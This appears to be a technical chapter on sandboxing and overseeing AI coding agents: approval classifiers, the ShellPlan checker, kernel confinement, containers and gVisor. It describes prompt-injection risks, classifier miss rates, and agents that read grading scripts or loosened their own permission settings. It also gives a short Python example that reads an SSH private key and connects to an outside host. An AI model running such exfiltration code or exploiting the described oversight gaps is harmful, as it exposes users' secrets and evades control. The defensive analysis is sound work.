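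To measure how well people review commands, Anthropic had a research vendor recruit 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what the study measured. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which would never run. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

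Auto mode's classifier blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%. In 110 sessions neither the tester nor the classifier would have stopped the command. The testers worked in an artificial environment with nothing of their own at stake, which may have made them careless, and Anthropic was promoting the classifier. But the decline within sessions is consistent with approval fatigue.

As Rice's theorem leads one to expect, the classifier blocks some harmless actions and allows some dangerous ones, and its designers could reduce one kind of error by accepting more of the other. Anthropic described its two stages in an earlier engineering post. The first gives only a yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags an action, the same model reasons about the action before deciding. On 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's employees, the first stage alone blocked 8.5% of harmless actions, and the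 two together blocked 0.4%. But on 52 real cases in which the agent had exceeded what its user wanted, adding the second stage raised the share of dangerous actions allowed from 6.6% to 17%. Because the sample is so small, the true rate with both stages could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented to it. For instance, a user had asked the agent to "clean up" some work without mentioning the destructive step the agent chose. Anthropic tried changing the classifier's instructions to correct this, but found no fix whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

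The classifier's input contains only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that the agent can't use them to influence the classifier's decision. It also removes tool output, where planted instructions usually arrive. This makes the classifier harder to manipulate but gives it less information. If an agent cancels a job that the user never named, the input doesn't show whether the agent found the job's identifier in a query or invented it. In the spreadsheet example, the input wouldn't show which files the script would remove.

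An outside test found a much higher miss rate. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* summarises a trial on 128 deliberately ambiguous system-administration scenarios, in which 81% of the dangerous actions got through. Many were file edits, and auto mode doesn't send edits inside the project to the classifier. The summary is second-hand and the scenarios were hard by design, so the figure isn't an estimate of the everyday rate. Still, the gap between 81% and 17% suggests that a classifier's miss rate depends heavily on which cases are tested.

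Anthropic doesn't present the classifier as a substitute for careful review of critical infrastructure, and its *Auto mode for Claude Code* still recommends isolated environments. *Help! My coding agent can run code* describes how Posit Assistant, its writers' own product, combines model review with a sandbox. Every command runs in the sandbox, and a model reviews a command only if the sandbox has refused it. The model then has far fewer decisions to make, and the sandbox limits what unreviewed commands can do.

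### Running exactly what the checker approved

Another weakness of command checkers is that two programs interpret the same text. In the usual design, the harness parses the command, applies its rules to the result, and hands the original text to a shell, which parses it again. If the two interpretations differ, the shell may do something the rules forbid.

In *ParseGap*, Li (2026) looked for such failures by passing each command to a vendor's unmodified checker and separately running it in Bash, inside an isolated container where monitors recorded the programs it started and the files it changed. Li found 17 distinct root causes across eight production coding agents, and every agent's checker allowed some commands whose effects violated the policy.

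Li's proposed remedy, ShellPlan, interprets the command once and runs that interpretation. Suppose an agent proposes `grep -i total reports/*.csv | sort`, which finds every line containing "total" in a folder of reports and sorts the lines. ShellPlan compiles the text into a *plan*, a tree with a node for each command. Here the plan is a pipeline with two nodes, `grep` and `sort`. Each node holds the program's name, its arguments, and any instructions to read from or write to a file. The compiler accepts only a strict subset of Bash. A plan can chain commands, connect them with pipes, or use one command's output as another's argument, but each program's name must appear as literal text. ShellPlan sends anything outside the subset to a person without running it.

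It then checks every node against the operator's policy. The policy must allow the program, and the program can't be an interpreter. Commands that call shells, Python or utilities that exist to launch other commands go to a person for review.

The arguments have to fit a *positive specification*, which lists the options and the number of arguments ShellPlan accepts for that utility. For `sort`, the specification leaves out options that would write a file or start another program. Unlike a denylist, a positive specification excludes any option its author didn't consider. Li wrote specifications for 20 common utilities, including Git's read-only commands. An earlier version of ShellPlan without these specifications admitted 32 of 55 test cases in which approved utilities had forbidden effects, so parsing the command correctly wasn't enough.

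Before running the plan, ShellPlan replaces `reports/*.csv` with the names of the matching files, as a shell normally would, then checks the resulting arguments again. It also confirms that each program's file lies outside the agent's workspace, so the agent can't substitute its own version of `sort`. If a command redirects its output to a file, ShellPlan checks the destination beforehand and again when it opens the file. Before running any Git command, it checks the repository's settings, because some can make Git start other programs.

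Finally, it starts each program with `execve`, a system call that takes a program and a list of separate arguments. The text never passes through a shell, and an approval never loosens the operating system's restrictions.

Li proves that if ShellPlan refuses a plan, none of the plan's commands runs, and that if it admits one, every process it starts directly is either a checked command or one of a few fixed, read-only tests. Li also proves a limit on which files an admitted plan can write, assuming the host is trustworthy and the utilities behave as specified.

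That theorem doesn't cover programs such as test runners, which execute the project's own code. When Li replayed recorded coding sessions under a policy that permitted a test runner, ShellPlan admitted 398 commands. Of these, 44 had effects beyond what a read-only policy and its stated exceptions allow, and all 44 were test runs. ShellPlan can predict effects because it removes general programs from the language, so the prediction no longer holds if the operator allows them back in.

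ShellPlan admitted none of the 4,174 commands with a forbidden effect in six collections of attack commands. Li also ran ten models on nine attack tasks and ten harmless ones, with no person available to approve anything. Four of the harmless tasks deliberately included requests for shell features that ShellPlan doesn't support. The table compares ShellPlan with no gate, the rules from the coding agent Roo Code, and a language model acting as judge.

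| Gate | Attacks that succeeded (of 90) | Ordinary development tasks completed (of 60) | Tasks asking for unsupported syntax completed (of 40) | Median checking time per task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 62 | 53 | 40 | none |
| Roo Code's rules | 56 | 45 | 39 | 2.1 ms |
| Model as judge | 6 | 50 | 37 | 6,062 ms |
| ShellPlan | 0 | 49 | 25 | 1.3 ms |

With ShellPlan, the models completed 74 of the 100 harmless tasks, compared with 93 without a gate. Fifteen of the 19 lost tasks came from the group designed to provoke refusals. The six frontier models usually found another way to do the work and completed 56 of their 60 harmless tasks, compared with all 60 without a gate. The four smaller models fell from 33 of 40 to 18. In a real deployment, a person could approve some of the refused commands, but that would bring back the approval prompts that people stop reading.

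The share of real commands that ShellPlan accepts depends on how an agent writes them. In recorded sessions on the programming benchmark SWE-bench Verified, it accepted 343 of 456 read-only steps. In sessions from another agent, OpenHands, it accepted none of 108, because that agent began every command by changing directory, which the compiler doesn't support. Of 1,523 shell commands that people had written for a separate dataset, it accepted 434. Li considers support for changing directory a clear extension, and it would probably allow many of the rejected steps.

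The security results are strong but come from a single-author preprint by Li, who also designed the defence and many of the attacks. None of the 90 attempts succeeded, but the true success rate for attacks like these could still be as high as about 4%. In two rounds of auditing, Li found 14 security flaws in earlier versions of ShellPlan, and the final version has one known weakness when it allows writing to the workspace. The study also excludes disclosure, so an approved command that reads a private file outside the workspace doesn't count as a violation. ShellPlan would need another control to protect the analyst's other files.

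### Programs that may call only listed functions

*Programmatic tool calling* lets the model write a program with loops and conditions, but the program can affect the outside world only by calling functions from the operator's catalogue. Vendors introduced it mainly for efficiency. Anthropic explained when it released the feature that a model calling tools one at a time has to run again after each call, and every intermediate result adds to the text it must process.

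Suppose a company wants to know which of 20 employees have exceeded their travel budgets. With ordinary tool calls, the model makes 20 requests and receives thousands of expense records. With programmatic calling, it writes one script that makes the 20 requests, compares the totals with the limits and returns only the names of those who overspent. On web-search benchmarks, Anthropic found that adding programmatic calling to its basic search tools improved performance by 11% on average and reduced input by 24%.

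In OpenAI's version, the program is written in JavaScript and runs on OpenAI's servers. Each program gets a fresh, isolated copy of V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine. According to OpenAI, this runtime has no direct network access, no general file system, and no means of installing packages or starting other programs. The developer decides whether the model may call each tool directly, from a program, or either way. When a program calls one of the developer's tools, the developer's own application still runs it, so the harness can check every call, including each repetition in a loop.

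Under these conditions the program has almost no authority of its own. By the reachable-effects argument, it can produce only the effects of the catalogued functions, alone or in combination, so the allowlist again accurately describes what the agent can do.

Anthropic's version instead runs the program in the same container as its general code execution tool, and the developer marks which tools the program may call. When the program calls one, the response pauses and Anthropic tells the developer which run made the call. The program continues once the developer returns the result. Because that container is still a code interpreter, an operator who wants the guarantee of a fixed catalogue has to check where the program runs.

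### The cost of removing the shell

If a restricted runtime were as useful as a shell, operators could drop the interpreter and lose little. *Is Bash All You Need?* (Mak, Suresh and colleagues, 2026), a study led from Microsoft, compared five ways of giving an agent its tools, using Anthropic's Opus 4.8 and OpenAI's GPT-5.5. One gave the agent only *typed tools*, individual functions with defined arguments, like the weather tool. Another gave it only a shell. A third combined a shell with typed tools, and a fourth combined a shell with a folder where the agent could save tools it wrote and reuse them in later tasks. The fifth, programmatic calling, used Python in a restricted runtime that had no shell and could act only through the typed tools.

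They tested each arrangement on two sets of office tasks. TheAgentCompany simulates a software company with 17 colleagues the agent can message. Its 174 tasks include screening job applicants and keeping two project-tracking systems in sync. APEX-Agents has 480 tasks from investment banking, management consulting and corporate law, mostly involving documents and spreadsheets. The table gives the average score out of 100, with the estimated model cost per task in brackets.

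| Interface | Software company, Opus 4.8 | Software company, GPT-5.5 | Professional analysis, Opus 4.8 | Professional analysis, GPT-5.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Typed tools only | 44.9 ($1.20) | 45.3 ($0.66) | 41.1 ($0.73) | 39.8 ($0.52) |
| Programmatic calling | 52.9 ($0.64) | 45.1 ($0.54) | 40.1 ($0.61) | 37.8 ($0.48) |
| Shell only | 69.4 ($0.37) | 67.1 ($0.56) | 48.5 ($0.48) | 44.6 ($0.40) |
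| Shell and typed tools | 67.2 ($0.55) | 66.3 ($0.60) | 47.2 ($0.60) | 45.5 ($0.42) |
| Shell and saved tools | 67.1 ($0.35) | 66.4 ($0.61) | 46.9 ($0.50) | 45.9 ($0.44) |

Agents with only the shell scored 21.8 to 24.5 points higher than agents with typed tools on the software-company tasks and 4.8 to 7.4 points higher on professional analysis. They also used 19 to 72% fewer tokens, the units of text that models process and vendors bill for. Adding typed tools or a folder of saved tools to the shell did not detectably change the score.

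Programmatic calling cost less than typed tools in every case, but scored clearly higher only for Opus 4.8 on the software-company tasks. Averaged over both models, it scored 3.5 points higher on those tasks and 1.5 points lower on professional analysis, a difference within the margin of error. Only 65% of its calls succeeded on the software-company tasks, against 92% for the shell. Mak and colleagues suggest that models struggle to coordinate several tool calls in one program and to handle failures partway through.

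These gaps estimate how much performance an operator would lose by removing the interpreter. The loss is largest in software engineering and close to zero in corporate law, where all five arrangements scored about the same. Part of the large gap may come from gaps in the tool catalogue more than from restricting agents to typed tools. TheAgentCompany came without typed tools, so the researchers wrote 60, which cover the services the tasks need but not everything a shell can reach. A more complete catalogue might narrow the difference, though an operator's own catalogue would have omissions too.

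*Help! My coding agent can run code* gives two reasons why continuing to add narrow tools doesn't solve the problem. Models tend to handle large numbers of tools badly, probably because their training data contains far more code than examples of choosing from a long list of tools. A coding agent also has to do things its developers didn't anticipate, which a fixed set of tools can't cover.

The study also found a drawback to keeping the shell. During development, agents with shell access sometimes took the answers from the benchmark's public grading scripts, or read the simulated colleagues' files instead of contacting them. Before the runs they report, the researchers blocked network access to the scripts' repository and encrypted the colleagues' files. They couldn't have fixed this by editing the tool list, since the shell was the only tool in some of these runs.

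In the professional-analysis tasks, the shell beat the typed tools even though it ran with restricted file access, limits on execution, and an environment without credentials and other settings. At least some of its benefit therefore remains when it is confined. Mak and colleagues recommend the shell where an operator can isolate it, and programmatic calling where security or compliance rules require a fixed catalogue.

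### Why a restricted runtime still needs a sandbox

Programmatic calling gives the operator a smaller language, but the runtime has to enforce that language's limits, and a flaw in the runtime could give a program all the authority of the process it runs in. The catalogue limits what a program can do while the runtime works correctly. If the runtime fails, a sandbox around the process limits the damage.

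A sandbox also handles behaviour that breaks no rule of the language. A program can loop forever or fill the machine's memory without calling any function. Because of the halting problem, no checker can identify every such program in advance, so the sandbox needs to limit time and memory.

CrewAI, a framework for building agents, once used a restricted form of Python as a fallback. Its built-in interpreter tool normally ran code in a Docker container with access to the current working directory. If Docker was unavailable, the tool switched to a Python environment that blocked many modules and built-in functions. It reported the switch in its printed output, but an operator who expected a container might have missed the message and relied on the weaker protection unknowingly. A third mode ran code directly on the host.

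CrewAI has since removed the tool from its library and deprecated the settings that let an agent run code. Developers who use CrewAI now have to choose a sandbox themselves, and CrewAI directs them to E2B or Modal, services that run code in dedicated sandboxes. Its notice gives no reason for the change, so the removal isn't evidence that the restricted Python failed.

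## Process sandboxes and containers

An operating system can confine a process without analysing the program it runs. Linux has several mechanisms for this, each restricting a different part of a process's authority. Coding agents combine some of them into a *process sandbox* around each command, and Docker combines much the same set into a container.

### The kernel's means of confinement

A *namespace* gives a group of processes its own version of some part of the system. In a new mount namespace, the processes see a file tree that the sandbox's builder assembled, which might hold a project folder, Python and little else. A process namespace hides the other running programs. A network namespace starts with no connection to the outside, and a user namespace can map its root account to an ordinary account on the host. Namespaces only control what a process can see, so if the builder leaves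 the home directory in the tree, the sandboxed code can use it.

*Control groups*, or cgroups, limit how much of the machine's resources a group of processes can use. If the guest exceeds its memory limit, the kernel kills one or more of its processes. If it uses up its share of processor time, the kernel slows it down. Neither limit stops an endless loop, so a harness still needs its own time limit.

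A sandbox can also drop privileges. A process running under a separate ordinary account can't open files that only another account may read. Some guests need root, for example to install packages. Linux divides root's power into several dozen privileges, such as loading code into the kernel, and the sandbox can withhold most of them. Another setting stops a process from regaining privileges by starting a program that normally runs as root.

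*Seccomp* restricts which system calls a process may make. *Shrinking the Kernel Attack Surface Through Static and Dynamic Syscall Limitation* (Zhan, Yu et al., 2025) describes how a process gives the kernel a small filter program, which the kernel runs on every later call. The filter receives the call's number and arguments, and can reject the call. When a program opens a file, the path argument is only a memory address, and the filter can't read the path stored there. It therefore can't block access to a private key without blocking every attempt to open a file, which would stop Python from starting.

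*Landlock* lets a process declare which directories it and its descendants may read or write, and the kernel refuses access to the rest. An ordinary program can do this without root, and neither it nor its children can later loosen the rules. Newer kernels also let Landlock restrict which TCP ports a process may use, but not which servers it connects to. *Sandlock* (2026) presents a sandbox in which Landlock enforces fixed rules about files and ports, seccomp blocks system calls that are never allowed, and a supervising program handles only the decisions that depend on what happens at run time.

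The macOS counterpart is *Seatbelt*. A launcher gives macOS a profile of permitted and forbidden operations, covering files and network connections, and macOS applies it to the process and its children.

### One program under each mechanism

Suppose planted instructions lead a coding agent to run this program under a developer's account:

```python
import socket
key = open("/home/dev/.ssh/id_ed25519").read()
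socket.create_connection(("192.0.2.10", 443))
```

The second line reads the private key she uses to log in to her employer's servers, and the third opens a connection to an outside machine. Without a sandbox, both succeed. The table shows the result of each attempt with only one mechanism in place, assuming the program continues after an error.

| Mechanism used alone | Reading the key | Opening the connection |
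|---|---|---|
| Mount namespace without her home directory | "No such file or directory" | succeeds |
| Network namespace with no outside connection | succeeds | "Network is unreachable" |
| Separate ordinary account | "Permission denied" | succeeds |
| Seccomp filter refusing internet sockets | succeeds | "Operation not permitted" |
| Landlock allowing only the project and system files | "Permission denied" | succeeds, unless the rules also cover ports |
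| Cgroup limits | succeeds | succeeds |
| Seatbelt profile denying both | "Operation not permitted" | "Operation not permitted" |

Blocking only the connection doesn't keep the key secret, because the program can print it to the model, and a tool outside the sandbox could then send it out. If only the file is blocked, the guest can still send out anything else it can read. Anthropic advises restricting both file and network access, partly because a guest that can write anywhere may be able to alter the system and regain network access.

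The program receives the same errors it would get from an ordinary fault, such as a missing file. *Permission Denied* (2026), an evaluation of coding agents in restricted environments, relies entirely on native mechanisms of this kind. Before each agent starts, the researchers run probes to confirm that permitted operations still work and that forbidden operations fail, as do attempts to get around the restrictions, including from child processes. If a required probe fails, they discard the run and start a fresh sandbox.

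Operators have good reason to run similar checks, because a missing sandbox may cause no errors. If Claude Code can't start its sandbox, for instance because a required package is missing, by default it runs commands without one. A setting makes it exit instead.

### Sandboxes on a developer's machine

A local coding agent runs many short commands on real project files. *Sandlock* notes that containers require images and configuration, and that microVMs need hardware support and take noticeable time to start. Local agents therefore mostly use the operating system's sandboxing mechanisms directly. On Linux, Codex and Claude Code use *bubblewrap*, a small program that creates namespaces, assembles a file tree and starts a command inside it. On macOS, both use Seatbelt.

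By default on Linux, Codex lets each command read the whole disk but write only to the workspace and temporary directories. Each command runs in its own user, process and network namespaces with a seccomp filter, and any program it starts inherits the same limits. Within the workspace, Codex keeps Git's internal folder and its own settings read-only. Claude Code similarly protects its settings files, since a command that could edit them might grant itself more permissions, as Amp's agent did.

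The Python program fails to open the connection in either sandbox under default settings, but it can read the key because both products let commands read most of the disk. Anthropic acknowledges that this includes credential files and supplies no built-in list of files to block, so the user has to name them. OpenAI's *Sandbox* explains how to make chosen paths unreadable in Codex. These defaults suit programming, where a build may need files from many places, but they are a poor fit for a machine that holds valuable keys.

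Sandboxing on Windows has lagged behind macOS and Linux. OpenAI built its own Windows sandbox for Codex because it found no suitable equivalent to Seatbelt or bubblewrap. Claude Code's sandbox doesn't run on native Windows, so commands run unconfined unless the developer uses Windows Subsystem for Linux.

### Eleven agent systems

Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues (2026) read the source code of eleven agent systems for *Harness Engineering*, mostly in their July 2026 releases. Only two of the systems shipped sandboxes for Linux, macOS and Windows.

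| Arrangement | Systems | What confines commands |
|---|---|---|
| Operating-system sandbox included | Codex, Gemini CLI | Bubblewrap, Seatbelt, or Windows processes with reduced rights; Gemini CLI also supports Docker, gVisor and LXC, another container system |
| Included, but the user must enable it | Claude Code | Bubblewrap or Seatbelt |
| Depends on the execution environment chosen | OpenHands, mini-SWE-agent, Hermes | Containers or remote machines; mini-SWE-agent also supports bubblewrap |
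| None built in | Mistral Vibe, Pi, OpenCode, Aider, OpenClaw | No operating-system boundary |

Some entries may already be out of date. The Claude Code entry is based on a source snapshot from March 2026, although Anthropic's documentation from October still lists the sandbox as off by default. In June, Google replaced Gemini CLI for consumers with a closed-source successor. By September, OpenClaw's documentation described its own sandbox.

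Larger agent systems do not always have sandboxes. In the study's April edition, the two largest systems were also the two with native sandboxes, but the July edition added Hermes and OpenCode, which each have more than half a million lines of code and no operating-system sandbox. Hermes instead scans files and tool descriptions for planted instructions, and blocks a short list of catastrophic commands even when the user has turned approvals off. OpenCode analyses the syntax of commands to decide which need approval.

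Pi's developers deliberately leave out a sandbox, arguing that a partial one inside the agent's own process "would be easy to misunderstand as a security boundary." That is a fair objection to weak protection, but Pi's tools run with the user's full authority until she adds a sandbox as an extension. Barbaste and colleagues compare designs but didn't test whether any of the sandboxes work.

### Tools and servers outside the sandbox

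Claude Code's sandbox covers shell commands but not the built-in file and web tools, which follow permission rules instead. If a developer blocks access to a key file only in the sandbox's settings, the file-reading tool can still open it. A permission rule that denies reading the file is safer, because Claude Code applies it to both the tool and the sandbox.

Two other kinds of program run outside the boundary with the developer's full access. *Hooks* are commands the developer sets to run automatically at certain points, such as after every file edit. Local *MCP servers* are separate programs that supply extra tools through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to services. When the model calls a tool on such a server, the server runs with its own permissions, even if the shell is restricted.

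In Codex, the sandbox also covers the built-in file operations, but connected applications and MCP tools go through approvals. Codex always requires approval for a call that the tool itself labels as destructive, so this protection depends on an accurate label. Web search is also separate from the sandbox, and by default it uses a stored index of pages that OpenAI maintains. On OpenAI's platform for hosted agents, some MCP connections start in the customer's environment, but others start from OpenAI's own service, where the environment's network rules don't apply.

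OpenClaw can use Codex as its engine, but the Codex process stays on the host even when OpenClaw's sandbox is on. OpenClaw therefore disables Codex's own code execution, the user's MCP servers and application plugins during sandboxed turns. Without the sandbox, OpenClaw's defaults give a local Codex session full access and no approval prompts, unless the machine's Codex policy forbids it.

*The Compiler May Read It, the Agent May Not* (2026) examines such gaps in a working deployment, where a research group wanted an agent to build a program without seeing part of its source code. It lists fifteen routes by which the protected text could reach the agent, and compares which routes the container, permission rules, sandbox and written instructions each cover. No check ran on some of the routes.

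A developer can close many of these gaps by running the whole agent inside a boundary. Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* lists as options a container, a virtual machine and Anthropic's sandbox runtime, which applies the same bubblewrap or Seatbelt restrictions to the entire Claude Code process. Anthropic considers the shell sandbox alone insufficient for fully unattended work. But the agent needs its login and some of its settings inside the larger boundary. If the session can write to those settings, it can leave behind a hook that runs unconfined the next time the developer starts Claude Code normally.

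### Approval must not remove confinement

An approved command must always stay in the sandbox, because people and rules sometimes approve harmful commands and the sandbox limits the damage. Outside it, a harmful command would run with the full authority of the user's account.

In the version of Codex that Li tested, allow rules removed the operating system's confinement even in read-only mode, because a single decision controlled both approval and confinement. Without those rules, none of Li's 83 test cases left a lasting change to the file system in the read-only sandbox. OpenAI's documentation describes rules as a way to allow certain commands outside the sandbox, but a developer who adds one to avoid repeated prompts may not realise that it also removes the confinement.

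Claude Code has a milder form of the same problem. When a command fails in the sandbox, the model may request a retry outside it, and an allow rule that matches the command also approves the retry. The developer can forbid these retries, or add a rule that overrides the allow rule and requires the user's approval for each one.

Modes that skip approval prompts raise the same issue. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) compares two such modes. One also drops the sandbox, which gives any planted instruction the user's full permissions. The other is safer because it keeps the sandbox and absolute refusals. Codex users can take the safer approach by turning off approval requests and keeping the workspace sandbox.

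Some tasks need commands that can't work inside a sandbox. Docker commands, for example, don't work in Claude Code's sandbox. Anthropic provides a list of exceptions but recommends first trying to grant the command the one extra directory or network host it needs. It also warns that an exception covering an interpreter, or a script the agent can edit, lets the agent write a program and run it outside the sandbox. If an exception is unavoidable, leaving the sandbox should be a separate request with its own prompt.

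### How containers work and what undoes them

Docker builds containers from the same kernel mechanisms. It normally starts them through *runc*, a program that creates the namespaces and cgroups, drops privileges, installs the seccomp filter and starts the guest's first process. A container gets its file tree from an *image*, a package containing its own programs and libraries, whereas the local sandboxes usually let a command see most of the real disk.

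In an ordinary Docker container, the Python program would get the opposite results from those in Codex or Claude Code. It would fail to read the key, because the developer's home directory isn't in the image, but it could open the connection, because Docker normally gives containers outbound network access. To block the connection too, an operator has to change the network settings.

Other settings can remove a container's existing protection. If the operator shares the home directory with the container, the key is available again. Privileged mode restores root's powers over the kernel and the machine's devices, and turns off the seccomp filter. Anthropic warns that giving the guest access to Docker's control socket, which programs use to create containers, effectively gives it control of the host.

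A container may block the operations that bubblewrap needs to sandbox an agent inside it. Claude Code has a weaker nested mode for this case, which Anthropic recommends only if the outer container already provides enough isolation. OpenAI suggests turning off Codex's inner sandbox and relying on the container when the two can't work together. A malicious project can then send out anything in the container, including Codex's credentials, if the network rules allow it, so OpenAI limits this advice to trusted repositories.

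### The shared kernel

Even a correctly configured container uses the host's kernel, so a flaw in that kernel can defeat every restriction the kernel enforces. Zhan and colleagues report that Docker's default filter blocks about 50 system calls and permits more than 250. Any permitted call may reach faulty kernel code, and a container that exploits the fault can gain control of the host. Process sandboxes such as Codex's have the same weakness.

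A virtual machine has its own kernel. Code that takes control of that kernel is still inside the virtual machine. To reach the host, it must exploit a second flaw, either in the software that runs the virtual machine or in the hardware.

Some sandboxes depend on a feature that exposes more of the kernel. Bubblewrap usually works only if ordinary accounts can create user namespaces, which let those accounts use kernel code otherwise reserved for root. Recent versions of Ubuntu restrict this for security reasons. Anthropic's instructions leave less of the kernel exposed because they make an exception for bubblewrap alone, while OpenAI's documentation of June 2026 gave a command that lifts the restriction for every program on the machine.

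Operators can reduce the exposure by permitting fewer system calls. Zhan and colleagues built a tool that analyses a program and its libraries to find which calls it needs, then checks doubtful calls as the program runs. They estimate that it protects each program against 71 known vulnerabilities on average. But this works best for a program that does the same job every day, such as a web server. A code interpreter has no fixed set of system calls, because the model may install and run almost anything, so a strict filter would block useful work.

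IBM's Nabla containers allow the guest only seven system calls, by moving most of the operating system's work into a library inside the container. Developers have to recompile their programs to use them, which is a serious obstacle for an agent that installs ordinary packages. gVisor and microVMs instead put another kernel between the guest and the host, and most programs can run unchanged.

According to Willison's *How we contain Claude across products*, Anthropic uses Seatbelt and bubblewrap to contain Claude Code on a developer's machine, gVisor for the Claude.ai service, and a full virtual machine for Cowork, its desktop agent.

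## gVisor: a kernel in user space

gVisor is a user-space kernel, an ordinary program that answers a guest's system calls in place of the host's kernel. Google developed it for its own services and published the code in 2018. In October 2026 the gVisor blog announced that the project was moving to the Cloud Native Computing Foundation, part of the Linux Foundation. Google's Cloud Run and DigitalOcean's App Platform use it to run containers that customers supply, according to gVisor's *Applications*. Operators usually install it as *runsc*, a program that Docker can use instead of runc to start a container.

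gVisor's main component is the *Sentry*, a kernel written from scratch in Go. According to the project's security introduction, the Sentry reimplements Linux's system calls, memory management, file systems, networking and process handling. It serves as the guest's operating system but runs on the host as an ordinary unprivileged process.

### One file read

Suppose an agent's Python tool runs in a gVisor container, and the operator has shared a project folder with it. The model writes the same line as in the earlier example, `text = open("notes.txt").read()`.

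Python tries to open the file with a normal Linux system call. Under gVisor's default method, *systrap*, a seccomp filter on the guest catches the call. The host's kernel then sends a signal to the thread that made the call, rather than allowing or refusing it, as gVisor's *The systrap platform* describes. A small handler in the guest's process receives the signal and passes the request to the Sentry. The processor briefly enters the host's kernel, but the kernel never carries out the guest's request.

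The Sentry looks up `notes.txt` in the guest's own file tree and checks whether the guest's account may read it. The file itself is on the host's disk, and the Sentry needs a second process, the *Gofer*, to reach it. Before any guest code ran, the Gofer assembled the container's file tree from the folders the operator had listed and gave up its access to the rest of the disk. The Sentry is confined to an empty directory, so it can't open a host file by path. Instead, it requests an open handle to each shared folder from the Gofer, then uses the project folder's handle to open `notes.txt` with its own host system call.

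The Sentry then gives Python a file number that is valid only in the Sentry's records. When Python asks to read from that number, the filter catches the call again. The Sentry reads the bytes from the host, copies them into Python's memory and lets the program continue. The host's kernel has opened and read a file, but the Sentry composed both calls, and the guest could not choose their options.

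Until 2023 the Sentry could not open files, which gVisor (2019) gave as an example of least privilege. It sent a message to the Gofer for every file operation, and the Gofer performed it. Google had designed this for remote file systems, to keep their credentials out of a sandbox that an attacker might take over. For files on the same machine, the messages mostly added delay. gVisor (2023) announced the present arrangement, *directfs*, as the new default. In the developers' tests, getting a file's details became more than twice as fast, a group of real workloads took 12% less time, and Ruby loaded 17% faster.

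Directfs is faster but gives up some protection, because the Sentry's own filter now has to permit calls that open files and create directories. The Sentry also needs the Gofer's privileges, including the power to override ordinary file permissions. The filter still permits these calls only if they don't follow symbolic links, which are files that point to another path. Attackers who took over the Sentry could use these calls, and Linux's file isolation would have to keep them inside the shared folders. Operators can turn directfs off to restore the older, slower arrangement.

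By default, gVisor lays an in-memory file system over the container's own files, so an agent's changes to them go into that layer and leave the image untouched. *Rootfs Overlay* (Ranjan, 2023) introduced this layer to avoid slow trips through the Gofer. Shared folders have no such layer, so an agent that edits `notes.txt` in the project folder changes the developer's real file.

gVisor's quick test command, `runsc do`, gives the guest read access to the host's whole file system, so a program in that sandbox could read the developer's private key. If Docker starts the container instead, the guest can access only the folders in the container's configuration.

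### One network connection

The program in the previous section also tried to connect to an outside machine. gVisor changes which software makes such a connection but does not block it.

When Python requests a network socket, the Sentry creates one in its own records. When Python then calls `connect`, the Sentry's network stack builds the first packet and writes it to a virtual network card, and the host forwards it like traffic from any other container. The reply arrives at the same card, the Sentry reads it and updates the connection's state, and Python's call returns. The host's kernel handles finished packets but never opens a socket for the guest.

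gVisor (2020) explained that networking could have weakened the security model significantly, which is why the developers wrote a separate stack instead of using the host's. That stack is less efficient than Linux's and lacks some of its more advanced ways of recovering from lost packets. Operators who need more speed can choose *host networking*, in which the Sentry may open sockets on the host, but this exposes more of the host's kernel. In either mode, the operator has to decide which addresses the guest may reach and enforce that outside gVisor.

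### Three ways to catch a system call

gVisor calls its method of interception a *platform*. The table combines what gVisor's *Platform Guide* and the security introduction explain about each.

| Platform | How it catches a call | Where it suits | Status |
|---|---|---|---|
| ptrace | Linux's debugging interface stops the guest at each call | Almost any machine, but slowly | Unsupported; default until mid-2023 |
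| systrap | A seccomp filter turns each call into a signal | Virtual machines, and hardware without virtualisation support | Default |
| KVM | The processor's virtualisation features separate the guest from the Sentry | Physical servers | Supported |

KVM is the part of Linux that runs virtual machines. On gVisor's KVM platform, the Sentry acts as both the guest's kernel and the software that manages the virtual machine, but it provides no virtual disks or other emulated hardware. This platform gives the best performance on a physical server. Inside a rented virtual machine, the outer machine has to handle a second level of virtualisation, so systrap is often faster.

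An administrator can switch gVisor's platform without changing the container, but the platforms differ in security because each relies on a different part of the host's kernel to catch the guest's system calls. A flaw in KVM could affect an operator who uses the KVM platform but not one who uses systrap.

Even gVisor's old ptrace platform differed from what people usually call ptrace sandboxes. Those sandboxes inspect each system call and let approved ones continue into the host's kernel. In a program with several threads, one thread can change a call's arguments after the check and before the kernel uses them. gVisor avoids this problem because it never lets the call continue into the host's kernel.

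### What the second kernel protects

gVisor's protective filter surrounds the Sentry, not the guest, so it doesn't have to allow for everything a code interpreter might run. The developers know which host calls the Sentry makes, so the same filter suits a calculator, a compiler or a program the model has just invented.

gVisor's *Security Model* sets the rule that no guest call passes directly to the host. Many guest calls don't lead to a host call at all. A program that asks for its own process number, for example, gets the answer from the Sentry's table of the guest's processes, and the host isn't aware of those numbers. If one guest process waits for data from another, the Sentry may use a host call to make it wait, but a different one from the call the guest made. Even starting a program or opening a connection works for the guest, although the Sentry's filter normally forbids the Sentry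 from doing either on the host.

gVisor's practical benefit is protection against flaws in Linux itself. The *Dirty Cow* flaw let an ordinary program take control of memory that belonged to the system, using only the kernel's normal interface. gVisor handles the guest's requests with an independent implementation of that interface, which is unlikely to contain the same mistake.

An attacker would usually have to exploit a flaw in the Sentry and then another in the host's kernel to run code on the host. The two share no code. The Sentry is written in Go, which prevents most of the memory errors behind serious flaws in kernels written in C. The developers keep the few parts that bypass Go's checks in separate files with distinctive names so that reviewers can find them.

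Go does not prevent every kind of flaw. The Sentry is a large kernel, and researchers have found serious mistakes in versions of it. *G-Fuzz* (Li, Chen and colleagues, 2024) describes a tool that generates sequences of system calls to reach a chosen part of gVisor's code. The tool outperformed Syzkaller, the leading tool for testing kernels in this way, on 58 of 59 targets. It also found several vulnerabilities at the Chinese company Ant Group, though some may have come from the company's own modifications to gVisor.

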